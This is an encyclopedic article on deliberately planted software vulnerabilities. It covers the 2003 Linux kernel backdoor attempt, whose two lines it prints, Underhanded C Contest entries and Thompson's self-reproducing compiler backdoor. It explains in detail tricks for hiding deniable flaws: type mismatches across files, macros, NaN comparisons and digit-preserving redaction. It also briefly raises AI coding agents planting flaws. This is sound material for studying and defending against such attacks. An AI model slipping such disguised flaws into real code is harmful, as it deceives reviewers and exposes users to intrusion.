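# Deliberately Planted Software Vulnerabilities, from Underhanded Code Contests to AI Coding Assistants

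## What is a planted vulnerability?

A planted vulnerability is a security flaw that someone deliberately puts into software and disguises as ordinary code or an honest mistake. Anyone who knows about the flaw can use it against any system that runs the software. Programmers have held contests in writing such code, and attackers have tried to insert it into real projects. One small and unusually well-documented attempt, in November 2003, targeted the Linux kernel, the core of the Linux operating system, which controls the hardware and what every other program may do.

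The kernel's developers then kept the master copy of its source code (the text that programmers write and that a machine translates into a running program) in a system called BitKeeper. Some of them disliked BitKeeper, so BitMover, the company behind it, also published a duplicate through an older system called CVS. On 4 November somebody altered the duplicate. The change added two lines to wait4, a function that a program uses to wait for something to happen:

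```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

This code gives administrator rights to any program that calls wait4 with this odd pair of options. In C, the language of the kernel, `uid = 0` sets the user number to zero, while `uid == 0` tests whether it is zero. User number 0 is "root", the administrator, who may read and change everything on the machine. A quick reader mistakes the assignment for a test and thinks the code returns an error when a program belonging to root calls wait4 with those options. The computer scientist Ed Felten judged in *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (Freedom to Tinker, 2013) that even an expert, reading casually, would see harmless error checking.

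The rest of the condition kept the trick from being noticed. C evaluates the second half only when the first half is true, and programs had no good reason to combine those two options, so the assignment didn't run in normal use. When it did run, its value was zero, which C treats as false, so the error line underneath was skipped and the attacker's program got its new rights without an error.

A mismatch between files exposed the attempt. Every night BitMover's machines computed checksums (short numbers derived from a file's contents) for the public CVS copy and compared them with those of a copy kept in-house. In *BK2CVS problem*, McVoy (2003), who ran the company, told the kernel developers' mailing list that each genuine change carried a pointer to its counterpart in BitKeeper, but the three newest entries for one file had none. The entries were under the user name of David Miller, a well-known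 kernel developer, who denied making them. About twenty minutes after the two lines were added, 58 lines had been deleted from the file and then restored, with a message apologising for work on the wrong file.

McVoy restored the file within a day and at first called the matter no big deal. People on the list worked out what the changed lines did only after another developer asked to see them. McVoy had posted the lines himself without noticing the single equals sign ("Good eyes, I missed that"). A few days later, a commenter on the news site LWN credited the many people who can read open code. McVoy, signing as lm (2003), called that nonsense in *One attempt thwarted*. He said hundreds of people could have spotted the lines, but a wary company's routine check caught them.

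It is less clear how close the lines came to reaching users. Linus Torvalds, who leads the kernel project, wrote in the thread under McVoy's message that they had no route into a release. He said changes reached him either by email, where those to core files were read through, or through BitKeeper, whose users did not work from the CVS copy. McVoy thought a CVS user could have submitted the lines as part of a legitimate change. Theodore Ts'o, another kernel developer, saw a risk if a distributor built its product from the CVS copy. He also worried that someone could email Torvalds a subtle "fix" under a forged name, buried among plausible changes. Debian, a Linux distributor, marks the flaw as never released in its entry *CVE-2003-1161*.

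### Bug, vulnerability, backdoor

A bug is a mistake that makes a program behave differently from how its author intended. A vulnerability is a flaw that lets someone break the software's security, and most vulnerabilities are bugs. A backdoor is a hidden way into a system that its owner did not agree to. In *Backdoor*, the forensics researcher Zdziarski (2016) proposed that a mechanism must meet three conditions to count as one: intent, consent and access. A support account that the owner knows about and has accepted is not a backdoor under a definition that depends on consent, even if the account is dangerous.

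A planted vulnerability is a backdoor that appears to be something a programmer could have written by accident. Security people sometimes call it a "bugdoor", which *On the critical path to implant backdoors* (2024) defines as a backdoor that can plausibly pass for a genuine bug. Many backdoors are not disguised this way. *Not In My Git Yard* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, 2026) describes one that no programmer would have written by accident. Around 2011, attackers broke into the server that distributed vsFTPd, a file-transfer program, and replaced the official release with their own version. Anyone who then entered a smiley face as a user name got a command line with full administrator rights.

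The most careful definitions come from Thomas and Francillon, in *Backdoors*. They break every backdoor into four parts, and the 2003 lines show each of them:

- The input source is where the attacker's signal arrives, here the options that a program hands to wait4.
- The trigger is the condition that the signal must meet, here the exact pair of options.
- The payload is whatever then raises the attacker's privileges, here the assignment of zero to the user number.
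- The privileged state is what the attacker ends up with, here a program running as root.

Thomas and Francillon then ask whether the step from trigger to payload is written out in the code. If it is, as with a hard-coded password, they call it an intentional backdoor. If the step works only through something that looks like a bug, and there are other grounds to suspect intent, they call it a deniable backdoor. Without such grounds, it counts as an accidental vulnerability. They say nobody can tell a deniable backdoor from an accidental vulnerability on technical evidence alone, because the code may be identical. The 2003 case fits this scheme a little awkwardly because the assignment is in plain view, and the only doubt is whether its author meant to type a second equals sign.

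### Why the planter wants an excuse

A planted flaw has plausible deniability if, once found, it can pass for an honest mistake. Somebody caught with an obvious backdoor loses their access, may lose their job or face prosecution, and gives the project a reason to search everything else they wrote. If the flaw looks like a mistake, however, the project fixes it and the author keeps contributing. The excuse only has to be believable, and it usually is, because programming errors are so common. Several readers of Freedom to Tinker's account remarked that typing `=` instead of `==` is an old and familiar mistake in C.

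The planter of the 2003 Linux backdoor could only partly excuse it as a typing error. InfoQ's *Linux Backdoor* (2013) noted that wait4 has no reason to deal with user IDs at all, which makes a typing error hard to believe. One of Felten's readers added that, with the second equals sign in place, the line would have forbidden a harmless combination of options only to the administrator, which serves no purpose. Another reader suggested that a tired developer had made the mistake and skipped the approval process. But the CVS copy was exported automatically from the master, so an honest developer had no reason to write to it directly.

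So the delivery was much harder to explain away than the code. If the same two lines had reached Torvalds inside a trusted developer's patch, the trail would have led to that developer, who could have truthfully denied knowing about them. Readers of LWN's *An attempt to backdoor the kernel* (2003) disagreed over whether this could have worked. One thought CVS would treat the foreign lines as the developer's own and include them in outgoing patches; another replied that this would not happen to anyone who used CVS correctly. Nobody has established who made the attempt, and Felten doubted that anyone would.

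Deniability also makes the statistics unreliable, because a planted flaw that is disguised well enough is recorded as a bug. GitHub, which hosts a large share of the world's source code, examined a random sample of 521 security advisories for *2020 State of the Octoverse* (2021) and tied 17% of them to explicitly malicious behaviour such as backdoor attempts. Thomas and Francillon modelled eleven backdoors from real products and found none of them deniable. Neither count could have included well-disguised flaws, so neither shows that such flaws are rare.

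### How a planted flaw differs from malware

Malware is software that exists to do harm, such as a virus or a program that steals passwords. In principle, a defender can find and delete it, for example by looking for a file that does not belong on the machine or a process that contacts a strange address. A planted vulnerability is a flaw inside a function that the program needs, and it may be only one wrong character or a missing check. The program works normally until someone sends the right input. *Towards a Backdoorless Network Architecture Based on Remote Attestation and Backdoor Inspection* (2020) gives the similarity between legitimate functions and backdoor functions as the reason backdoors are harder to detect than malware. An intruder who gets in through the flaw often installs malware, and an investigator who removes the malware may leave the flaw in place.

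### From the author to the user

Several people handle a change to a program before it reaches users. A programmer first edits the source code and records the edit as a commit, with a name, a date and usually a short explanation. The project's repository stores all commits in order, so anyone can look up when a line appeared and under whose name.

In most serious projects, the commit then goes to code review, where someone other than the author reads the added and removed lines, asks questions and may demand corrections. A maintainer, a person with authority to accept changes into the project, makes the final decision. Reviewers mostly look for errors and assume that the author is honest.

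Automated tools check the change too. Typically they run a compiler, which translates the source code into a program, then run a set of tests and sometimes feed the program random inputs for about ten minutes to see if it crashes. A backdoor need not crash anything, and Kokkonis and colleagues state that such checks cannot detect a hidden password, for example. *Static Detection of Application Backdoors*, by Wysopal and Eng, describes ways to find backdoors with static analysis, the automatic checking of source code without running it. Developers in McVoy's thread had already noticed limits to this approach in 2003. Compilers can warn about a single equals sign in a condition, but one developer noticed that the parentheses around `current->uid = 0` switch that warning off. (C requires parentheses there, so they prove little about intent.) Another developer suggested scanning the kernel for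 every use of the `current` record, then conceded that a clever programmer could reach the same data by a path too complicated for the scan to follow.

Once the source code is accepted, a machine builds the software by translating the code into the form that computers run and packaging it. The project publishes the package as a release, which users download directly or get through a distributor. Nearly all software also contains dependencies, components written by other people, each with its own authors, reviewers and builds. A supply-chain attack reaches its victims through a component, tool or update they trust. The table below draws on *Supply chain threats*, which gives a real incident for each point of entry and is part of SLSA, a set of supply-chain security guidelines.

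| Stage | How a flaw can enter | A known incident |
|---|---|---|
| Writing | The producer or an author puts it there | The makers of SpySheriff sold malicious software as protection against spyware |
| Review | The reviewer misses it, or nobody reviews the change | A contractor at SushiSwap, a cryptocurrency project, redirected funds with a commit that a second reader could have caught |
| Repository | An intruder adds a commit to the stored code | Attackers broke into the server of the programming language PHP and inserted two commits |
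| Build | An intruder alters the program while a machine assembles it | Attackers made the build system of SolarWinds, a software company, insert malicious behaviour each time |
| Release | An intruder swaps the finished package | Attackers used leaked credentials to upload a malicious file to the place from which Codecov's users download |
| Dependency | Any of the above happens to a component | An attacker who controlled a component of event-stream published a malicious version without changing its source |

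Most of these incidents involved openly malicious code, but a disguised flaw can take the same routes. Reviewers never see a flaw that enters after review, and GitHub's *2020 State of the Octoverse* reports that attackers often bypass the repository for this reason. But such a flaw makes what users receive differ from what the project approved, and an automatic comparison can detect the difference, as BitMover's did. A flaw that enters at the writing stage and survives review creates no such difference. Every later step copies it, and a certificate that the package matches its source will be correct. SLSA states that its guidelines do not directly address a malicious producer.

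### Who could plant one

Insiders have the easiest start because employees and contractors can already change the code, know which parts their colleagues read closely, and have many innocent reasons to edit those parts. The company itself may also be responsible. *ROSA* (2025) mentions dubious developers who sell components containing backdoors, some deliberate and others forgotten access points from testing.

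Outside contributors can also plant vulnerabilities in open-source projects, which publish their code and accept help from strangers. A contributor can send useful work for months before sending anything harmful. The attacker behind the 2024 backdoor in xz, a widely used compression tool, became a maintainer this way. Stealing access is faster. In 2018 attackers hijacked the account of a maintainer of ESLint, a popular tool for checking code, and the 2003 intruder evidently got into the CVS server, though nobody learned exactly how.

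A state can use any of these routes because it can pay an insider, place a contributor or break into a server, and it has the resources to wait. Felten considered whether the US National Security Agency was responsible and answered "maybe", adding that many others had the skill and the motive. The maker of a programming tool has unusual reach, because a rigged compiler or build system could alter every program that passes through it.

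AI models now belong on the list too. A coding agent is an AI model that edits files, runs commands and tests code with little human help. It writes code that a human would once have written, and its changes go through the same review and build. It could plant a flaw because an outsider had tampered with its training or the material it reads. Unlike the others on the list, it could also, at least in principle, plant a flaw that no person wanted.

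## What did the programming contests show about hiding flaws in readable code?

Since 2004 programmers have competed in public at writing underhanded code, which looks clear and innocent but does something harmful. Their entries are rare examples of planted flaws whose authors admit to planting them. Entrants also usually explain their tricks, whereas nobody could ask the author of the 2003 kernel lines how he or she had chosen them.

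These contests are easy to confuse with the older International Obfuscated C Code Contest, which Landon Curt Noll and Larry Bassel founded in 1984 and which still runs. It rewards obfuscated code, which is openly unreadable. One winner fit a flight simulator into a page of symbols. A reviewer would reject such code on sight in a real project, so obfuscation is a poor way to hide a flaw. Contests for code that looks harmless began twenty years later.

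### Miscounting votes

Around the 2004 US presidential election, *The Obfuscated V contest* (Horn, 2004) invited programmers to write a vote counter that looked correct but favoured one candidate. Despite the contest's name, the code had to be believable. The program received a string of letters (K for Kerry, B for Bush and N for Nader) and printed the totals. Horn supplied an honest version to start from. Entrants could make the program miscount all the time or only on election day, 2 November.

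The judges read the programs first and picked the one that looked most correct. Then they ran it. If it miscounted, it won; otherwise, they moved on to the next. Programs in the election-day category also had to give a correct count on 1 November. Horn offered bonus points for keeping the total number of votes right, because a wrong total would reveal the fraud.

Paul Parkanzky won the election-day category with a program that relied on the word "second" being longer than "first" or "third". On the second of the month, the text overran the memory set aside for it, which shifted votes to Bush. Michal Zalewski won the other category with a program that gave Bush a tenth of the votes on any day.

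Horn gave 41 entries marks out of ten for creativity, believability and accuracy of the count. Seven entrants used the letter l in place of the digit 1, and five of them scored 4 or less. An entry that used `=` in place of `==`, as the 2003 kernel lines did, scored 3.3. These marks suggest that the judges found the classic typing errors unimpressive, but they don't measure how many readers would have missed each trick, because each mark combines three qualities.

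### The Underhanded C Contest

Scott Craver, a professor of information security at Binghamton University, was one of the seven who used the letter l. He started the Underhanded C Contest the following year. In the contest's *FAQ*, he credits Horn's contest and recalls being impressed that even a short program for counting characters could fail on one day, a flaw that testing would not reveal. He ran the contest eight times between 2005 and 2015, with a gap of more than three years after the 2009 round opened.

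Each round gave entrants a simple programming task and a harmful behaviour to hide in the code. Underhanded C Contest's *The 2015 Challenge* (2015) gives the scoring rules. Shorter and more readable programs earned more points, because a flaw is harder to hide in them. (Under the 2007 rules, reproduced in Shostack + Friends Blog's *Weak Crypto Contest* (2007), a source file of more than 200 lines was unlikely to win.) Tricks that fooled the reader's eye counted as much as deep technical ones. Entrants earned extra points for a plausibly deniable bug, and for code that still looked innocent under syntax colouring, which shows numbers, text and comments in different colours. The harmful behaviour had to be easy for an attacker to trigger, but should rarely occur by accident.

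Entrants put their explanations in a separate file so that the judges could first read the code without knowing the trick. Craver also gave points for humour and spite, such as hiding a flaw inside an error-checking routine. This probably explains why so many entrants hid their flaws in validation or logging code, so their choices are not good evidence that real attackers favour the same places.

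| Year | Task | Hidden harm | The winner's method |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2005 | Process an image | Put a secret fingerprint in every output | Two winners: a blur filter that picks up leftover memory, and machine code stored as a list of numbers |
| 2006 | Count the words in a text | Run very slowly on one operating system | A loop that measures the whole text again at every step |
| 2007 | Encrypt a file | Leave 0.01% to 1% of files easy to crack | A wrong declaration of the clock function |
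| 2008 | Black out parts of an image | Leave the hidden parts recoverable | A zero in place of every digit |
| 2009 | Print luggage-routing records | Lose a record when a clerk types a certain comment | A missing comma |
| 2013 | Measure how closely two users of a social network are linked | Make the attacker appear close to everyone | Two files that give one number different sizes |
| 2014 | Copy posts that match a secret surveillance order | Let the user find out | A macro that repeats its input |
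| 2015 | Compare a warhead's radiation with a reference | Accept a fake | Two files that give one number type different sizes |

### Places to hide a flaw

Three of these winners exploited how C handles programs with more than one file. The compiler translates each file separately, and the tool that joins the results matches functions by name without checking that the files use the same types of data. The 2007 winner declared `time`, the standard function that reads the clock, as taking no input. According to Underhanded C Contest's *The 2013 Challenge* (2013), `time` then altered whatever was in memory where its input should have been.

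Alex Olson won in 2013 with a similar mismatch in 54 lines. His program checks whether a moderator has invalidated an account. One file stores the answer as a four-byte `int`, but the other writes it as an eight-byte `long`. The extra four bytes overwrite the stored distance between the two users. For most accounts they are zero and have no effect. But if the account's name sorts before the text "!!INVALID!!", they set the distance to the closest possible value. A user called "!!!" with no friends therefore gets full access to everyone's account.

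Number formats can also hide flaws. The usual 32-bit whole number runs from −2,147,483,648 to 2,147,483,647, so the lowest value has no positive counterpart, and the function that computes absolute values commonly returns it unchanged. Gaëtan Leurent, a runner-up in 2013, used this to make a chosen user name point to position −2 of a table, just before its start, where the program stored the distance. Reviewers would have seen a line in his source code that resets any negative position to zero. But the compiler deleted that line while optimising the program, because the rules of C allow compilers to treat absolute values as never negative.

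Programs also reuse memory, and C does not clear it between uses. Natori Shin, one of the 2005 winners, wrote a program that blurs an image using a square grid of weights but fills in only a circle within the square. The corners keep what an earlier function left there, which is information about the image file, such as its owner and creation date, and these leftover values subtly change the blur. Underhanded C Contest's *The 2005 challenge* explains that nobody can read the information directly from the picture, but anyone who guesses it can test the guess. The compiler gives no warning because the code fills part of the grid.

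Another entry, from the 2007 contest, destroyed data in memory while running RC4, a cipher that repeatedly swaps the entries of a table. It made the swaps with an old trick that needs no spare variable but sets an entry to zero when swapping it with itself. A commenter on a post by the security writer Bruce Schneier (2008) quoted the contest's explanation that the zeros gradually poison the table. It would be easy to believe a programmer who called this a mistake, since many people have used the same trick to look clever.

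Macros can mislead a reader because they look like functions. A macro is a name that the compiler replaces with code before translating the program. The Swedish programmer Linus Åkesson took third place in 2008 with a macro for the number of bytes per pixel that lacks one pair of parentheses. As a result, `BYTESPERPIXEL(256 > max)` always gives 3 and `BYTESPERPIXEL(max < 256)` always gives 6, although the two conditions are equivalent. His program reads three bytes per pixel and writes six, so the file contains the original picture after the redacted one.

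Craver (2009), in *2008 Winners*, drew a principle from Åkesson's entry: "make the common case evil, and the uncommon case wrong". Nearly all images in this format use one byte per colour, and the macro appears to add support for the rare ones that use two. This apparent support gives the leaking code a plausible purpose. The program fails completely on two-byte images, but few people ever try one.

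Karen Pease's winning program of 2014 was more complicated. The standard macro that tests for a leap year evaluates its input up to three times, and her input was a macro that writes to an audit log. According to the Underhanded C Contest's *Review of the 2014 Challenge*, the repeated writes overfill the 16 bytes set aside for the log, and a later write then zeroes the user's account creation date. The date is zeroed only for users under surveillance, who can check it to learn that they are being watched. The flaw seems harder to pass off as a mistake than Olson's, since an investigator would have to believe that several unlucky choices were all accidental.

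The 2006 task called for a program that behaved differently on different platforms. The Underhanded C Contest reported that many entrants exploited the fact that processors store the bytes of a number in different orders. The winner instead used a loop that plenty of honest programmers have written. The loop, as printed in Shostack + Friends Blog's *2006 Underhanded C Contest* (2006), measures the length of the text again for every character. C finds that length by counting from the start, so a text ten times as long takes about a hundred times as much work. The Linux compiler moved the measurement out of the loop, but the Windows compiler did not.

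Sam Blackburn's winning entry from 2009 relied entirely on readers overlooking a missing comma. The program replaces swear words in the comments on luggage records with milder versions from a list. Where the list lacks a comma, C joins the two neighbouring pieces of text, so the program replaces "damn" with nine characters instead of four. The longer text can run past the end of the comment and into the flag that marks the record as deleted.

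Craver (2013), in *2009 Winners!*, liked that both the programmer and the airline clerk who types the word have an excuse. He contrasted this with an entry that the clerk could trigger only by typing something that was obviously an attack. A programmer may therefore be able to deny planting a flaw deliberately even when the person who triggers it can't deny using it deliberately.

RHays, a runner-up that year, wrote a comparison function that tests for the character `0` where it should test for `\0`, the marker that ends a piece of text. The function also contains unnecessary conditions. Craver thought they set up a repeating pattern that carries the eye past the error and make the author look like a beginner, so the clumsy code may be part of the disguise.

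### The 2008 winner: a redaction that kept its digits

The task in 2008 was to black out rectangles in an image, as officials do with names in scanned documents, while leaving a way to recover what was there. The contest received more than 100 entries, a record for the contest. Many entrants scrambled the pixels with a mask they could later reconstruct, or let the original data leak onto the end of the file, where most image programs ignore it. Both methods can look suspicious, because scrambling pixels is odd when the program could simply erase them, and somebody may notice the extra data.

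John Meacham's 55-line program does erase the pixels. It works on a version of the PPM image format that stores the picture as readable text, with three numbers between 0 and 255 for the strength of red, green and blue in each pixel. The program copies the file one character at a time, replacing each digit inside the rectangle with a `0`.

The number 255 becomes 000, 64 becomes 00 and 7 becomes 0. An image viewer treats all three as zero and draws black, but the file still contains the number of digits in each original value, which places that value in one of three ranges. The table below follows a row of six grey pixels, with one number for each pixel because the three colour numbers in a grey pixel are equal.

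| | Pixel 1 | Pixel 2 | Pixel 3 | Pixel 4 | Pixel 5 | Pixel 6 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Original value | 255 | 0 | 255 | 180 | 64 | 7 |
| Text in the redacted file | 000 | 0 | 000 | 000 | 00 | 0 |
| Colour on the screen | black | black | black | black | black | black |
| What the file gives away | 100–255 | 0–9 | 100–255 | 100–255 | 10–99 | 0–9 |

A photograph loses most of its detail this way, because 156 of the 256 possible values fall into the top band. Black-and-white text loses nothing, because its pixels have only two values, 0 for ink and 255 for paper, which become 0 and 000. Anyone with the file can recover the words exactly by turning every 000 back into white and every 0 into black. If the scan contains shades of grey, the recovered letters have rougher edges. The rules did not require the text to be even this legible. The Underhanded C Contest pointed out that an attacker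 may already know that the hidden word is one of two, in which case a faint trace is enough to decide between them.

Meacham's method also leaves the file size unchanged, which Craver counted in its favour. A check for appended data finds nothing. However, the unchanged size is itself a sign of the leak, because a program that wrote a single zero for each number would produce a smaller file.

In a comment under the results, Meacham added that the program had great deniability. He had a respectable engineering reason for the design that caused the leak. Working character by character avoided a problem with `fgets`, the standard C function for reading a line, and a version without the leak would have been more complicated or had bugs of its own. The method works only with the text version of the format, and anyone who opens the output in a text editor can see the pattern.

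### The 2015 winner: a warhead check with two kinds of number

The Nuclear Threat Initiative, a non-profit that works to reduce the danger from nuclear and other weapons, sponsored the contest's last round. The scenario was that two imaginary countries had agreed to dismantle warheads. An inspector had to confirm that each warhead was real, but a full scan would reveal secrets of its design, so the countries agreed on a program that would compare the scan with a reference and answer only yes or no. Entrants had to write the comparison so that the host country could pass off a fake warhead as real.

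The scan is a gamma-ray spectrum, a long row of counts showing how much radiation arrived at each energy. Plutonium produces a characteristic pattern of peaks. Åkesson, who had come third in 2008, wrote 66 lines in three files. His innocent-looking documentation describes a sensible detector. It first checks that the test object gives off enough radiation in total. It then smooths both spectra and replaces each value with its difference from the next, which removes the sloping background. After smoothing them again, it uses a standard formula to compare their shapes, where a score of 1 is a perfect match. He suggested accepting any score above about 0.6.

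The trick depends on the name `float_t`. Åkesson's own header file, which holds shared definitions, defines it as a `double`, an eight-byte number. The file that compares the shapes does not include this header, but it does include the standard mathematics header, where `float_t` usually means a `float`, a four-byte number. Neither source file includes both headers, so the compiler never processes the two definitions together and reports no conflict. As a result, one file passes a row of eight-byte numbers and the other reads them as four-byte numbers.

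Åkesson explains the effects in a separate file. The simplest is that the function compares only half the spectrum. It receives the right number of values to read, say 1,000, but reads only four bytes for each instead of eight, so it stops after 4,000 of the 8,000 bytes. Peaks in the right half therefore do not affect the shape comparison.

The left half still produces sensible results because of how a `double` stores small whole numbers. A computer stores a number with a fractional part as a sign, an exponent that gives its scale, and a mantissa that holds its digits. A `double` has 1 bit for the sign, 11 for the exponent and 52 for the mantissa, and the digits fill the mantissa from the left. Radiation counts are whole numbers, and Åkesson assumed that they stay below a million. Such a number needs no more than 20 binary digits, so the last four bytes of the `double` contain only zeros.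 The comparison reads every value as two numbers, and the one made from those last four bytes is zero in both spectra, so it doesn't affect the result.

The smoothing could have spoiled this by producing long fractions, so Åkesson averaged over 16 values, since dividing by a power of two changes only the exponent. He also designed the steps so that most terms cancel. These choices look like ordinary engineering, and the documentation gives an ordinary purpose for each stage.

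The cheating happens in the number made from the first four bytes. A `float` has only 8 bits for its exponent, so three bits of the original exponent end up in the mantissa. Cutting three bits off the exponent divides it by eight, which is roughly the same as taking the eighth root of the number. For example, 10 becomes about 2.56, 100 becomes 3.39 and 1,000 becomes 4.48. A peak ten times as high comes out only about a third higher, so the comparison still depends on where the peaks are but hardly on how large they are.

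A host country can therefore remove most of the plutonium and leave a little, so that small peaks remain in the expected places. It can then add another radioactive material with a strong peak in the right half of the spectrum. That material satisfies the check on total radiation, and the shape comparison never reaches its peak.

Åkesson tested the idea on 1,000 artificial materials, replacing 90% of each with a random substitute. Many of these crude forgeries failed. He said this hardly matters because the host can choose the best one. The forged spectrum he drew as an example passed at any threshold up to 0.72, above the 0.6 his documentation recommended.

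Craver (2016), in *Results of the 2015 Underhanded C Contest*, noted that a reader who misses the confusion of types will find nothing else suspicious in the program. The programmer could hardly have a better excuse, because the flaw looks like one forgotten line. However, the flaw depends on the machine. On 32-bit PCs running Linux, `float_t` has a third meaning and the program breaks.

The Nuclear Threat Initiative sponsored the contest. In its *“Underhanded C” Contest Highlights Challenges For Nuclear Arms Control Verification Technologies*, vice-president Page Stoutland said that such a program could let states take credit for disarmament without disarming. The organisation added that no standards existed for writing and reviewing code for arms control verification.

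### NaN poisoning

About a third of the more than 40 entries in 2015 used a different trick, based on a special value called NaN, for "not a number". Computers store it as the result of a calculation with no meaningful answer, such as zero divided by zero or the square root of −1. Most calculations that include a NaN also produce one, so it spreads. Checking whether a NaN is less than or greater than something always gives false.

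A programmer can exploit this through the order of the final test. Many entries ended with a line like this, where 1 means that the warhead is genuine:

```
return (detection_score < threshold ? 0 : 1);
```

The line rejects the warhead if the score is below the threshold and accepts it otherwise. This works for ordinary numbers, but if the score is NaN, the comparison is false and the program accepts the warhead. A safe version would accept the warhead only if the score is at or above the threshold. Both versions give the same result for every real number, so testing with ordinary data would not reveal the difference.

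The harder part is producing the NaN. Peter Eastman's program subtracts the normal background radiation and turns negative results into zero. A test object that never rises above the background leaves only zeros, so the formula divides zero by zero. But experienced C programmers look for a missing check before a division, and Craver thought this oversight would attract attention. Michael Dunphy's entry contains a check, which sets an error flag inside a function. Because a single `&` is missing, the function changes only a copy of the flag, and the error never reaches the rest of the program.

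Ghislain Lemaur hid the source of his NaN ("not a number") in the logging code. A message of exactly the right length overruns its buffer by two bytes and slightly changes a neighbouring number, the exponent 2.0 in a squaring formula. The log still prints the exponent as 2.0, but it is no longer a whole number, so raising a negative number to it gives NaN. The host country triggers this by giving the log file an owner with a five-digit user ID, which makes an error message just long enough.

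Most NaN entries missed the shortlist because the entrant assumed that the host could tamper directly with the input, the unchecked calculation was too blatant, or the conditions were too contrived. Philipp Klenze did better because a country could build something to trigger his flaw. His formula fails when one energy level has at least 1,686 counts. To reach that count, he proposed packing the fake with a short-lived radioactive material or hiding an X-ray device in it.

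Craver preferred flaws that the test object itself could trigger. Other entries required someone to interfere with the computer, for example by changing its clock or the number of processors available during the calculation. Inspection experts told the organisers that such interference could not be ruled out entirely, since the host may have physical custody of the machines. Still, a flaw triggered by the input alone, as Åkesson's was, requires less of the attacker.

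### Other languages and cryptography

Craver chose C because it gives programmers so many ways to make low-level mistakes. Other organisers have run underhanded contests for Solidity, a language for programs on the Ethereum blockchain, and for Rust, whose compiler rules out many of the memory errors that C permits. A stricter language, whose compiler checks types across files, would stop Olson's and Åkesson's tricks but not Meacham's, because replacing digits with zeros is valid code in almost any language.

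The Underhanded Crypto Contest focused on encryption. Hornby's *Second Underhanded Crypto Contest* describes the edition held at the Defcon 23 hacker conference in 2015, which drew five entries. One task was to change GnuPG, a widely used program for encrypting and signing messages, so that a message would leak the owner's private key. Joseph Birr-Pixton won this category by exploiting the way GnuPG 1.4 produces the random number used in each DSA signature. If that number is predictable, or not random enough, anyone can calculate the private key from the signature. Changing an existing program that people relied on is closer to a real attack than writing 60 lines from scratch.

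### The limits of contest evidence

The C programs are tiny and stand alone. Contestants did not have to fit them into older code, pass a project's tests or tell a colleague why the change was needed. But a reader can also study each line more closely than anyone studies the code of a large project. It is hard to say which difference matters more, so a contest result is not a reliable guide to how the same trick would fare in the Linux kernel.

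Judges, unlike ordinary reviewers, know that every program contains a trick. That makes them harder to fool, but at least one entrant succeeded. Domenico Andreoli's 2014 surveillance program was extremely short and readable, and the judge stared at it for some time without finding the bug. The answer was in a comment about a function that Andreoli had left out. That function downloads the user's picture from a web address the user supplied, so a user who watches that address learns of the surveillance.

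But this is an anecdote, and the contests provide no catch rate, the share of planted flaws that a reviewer finds. The judges could turn to the explanations when they were stuck, though some entrants in 2013 gave them no hints, and the published results do not record how many flaws the judges found unaided. Exercises such as Hack-a-Vote, in which students searched for flaws that other students had planted in voting software, come closer to measuring a catch rate.

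Failed entries have been studied much less than winners. The 2008 results describe only three of more than 100 programs in detail. Horn's marks for 41 entries are an exception, and David Wheeler later drew on Horn's contest in a study of countermeasures. The winners alone do not show whether programs with mismatched types won three times because reviewers rarely spot the mismatch or because many skilled entrants happened to try it.

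## Can a flaw be hidden where reading the source code will not reveal it?

The flaws in the contest programs were all in the source code, so a patient enough judge could find them. An attacker can also leave the source clean and put the flaw only into the finished program that the machine runs. Ken Thompson, one of the creators of Unix, explained how in October 1983, when he accepted the Turing Award. His method exploits the compiler. Programmers have to compile the compiler too, and they usually do so with an earlier copy of it.

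### A compiler that reinfects itself

In *Reflections on Trusting Trust*, Thompson (1984) describes how he altered the C compiler to look for a pattern that occurs in the source code of login, the Unix program that checks passwords. When the compiler found the pattern, it produced a login program that accepted either the user's real password or one that Thompson knew, so he could enter the system as any user. The change was not visible in login's source code, but it was visible in the compiler's, and Thompson conceded that even a casual reader of the compiler's source would become suspicious.

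Thompson therefore added a second pattern, taken from the compiler's own source code. When the altered compiler finds this pattern, it inserts both tricks into the new compiler it is building. Thompson described compiling this version once, installing it as the official compiler and deleting both tricks from the source. Anyone who then uses the installed compiler to compile the clean source gets a compiler that still contains both tricks.

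| After this step | Compiler's source | Compiler in use | Source of login | Login in use |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Add the login trick | Shows the trick | Contains it | Clean | Backdoored |
| Add the compiler trick | Shows both | Contains both | Clean | Backdoored |
| Restore the original source | Clean | Contains both | Clean | Backdoored |

The code inserted by the compiler trick has to reproduce its own text, because it must include the instructions for inserting itself again. A program can do this by storing its text as data, with a gap where the data belongs, and printing the text with a copy of the data in the gap. Such a program can reproduce any amount of extra code along with itself.

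Thompson used an innocent example to show how a compiler can contain information that is no longer in its source. Suppose a programmer wants C to accept `\v` as a name for the vertical tab, whose character number is 11. The existing compiler does not accept `\v`, so the programmer first writes the number 11 into the compiler's source, compiles it and installs the result. The new compiler accepts `\v`, so the programmer can now replace the 11 in the source with `\v`, leaving the number only in the compiled program.

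Thompson kept his code, and at a conference in March 2023 he said nobody had ever asked him for it. Russ Cox, a programmer who worked on the language Go, then asked. He published the code with notes in *Running the “Reflections on Trusting Trust” Compiler* (Cox 2023) and dated it to between June 1974 and June 1975. The code is 99 lines of C and a 20-line script. It only edits text, though Cox had expected something that worked deep inside the compiler. The code finds one distinctive line of login as the compiler reads it and adds text to the end, but it does nothing if a programmer asks to see the text at that stage.

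Cox ran the code in a simulator of an early Unix. The clean compiler took up 10,724 bytes and the backdoored one 12,918. When he used the backdoored compiler to compile the clean compiler source, the result was again 12,918 bytes. He then compiled login from its clean source and logged in as the administrator with the password "codenih".

Thompson had also tried the backdoor on colleagues. According to Cox, another group at Bell Labs copied the compiler, and in time their login program acquired the backdoor too. A mistake by Thompson made the compiler grow each time it compiled itself. The group noticed this and eventually broke the copying mechanism. On *David A. Wheeler's Page on Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, the security researcher quotes a 2021 message in which Thompson says he is not sure that they ever realised what was going on. Cox rejects an old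 rumour that the backdoor escaped from Bell Labs and let someone log in elsewhere as "kt", partly because the code only adds a password to accounts that already exist.

### The Air Force report behind it

Thompson credited the idea to an "Unknown Air Force Document". This was a security evaluation of the Multics operating system by Paul Karger and Roger Schell, which the US Air Force published in 1974. Unix took many of its concepts from Multics. Karger and Schell advised hiding a trap door, their term for a backdoor, in the compiled program, where no listing of the source would show it. Recompiling the source would remove it, so they proposed putting another trap door in the compiler. This one would recognise the most privileged parts of Multics and add a trap door to each. It could also preserve itself when the compiler was recompiled, because the compiler was written in PL/I, the language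 it translated.

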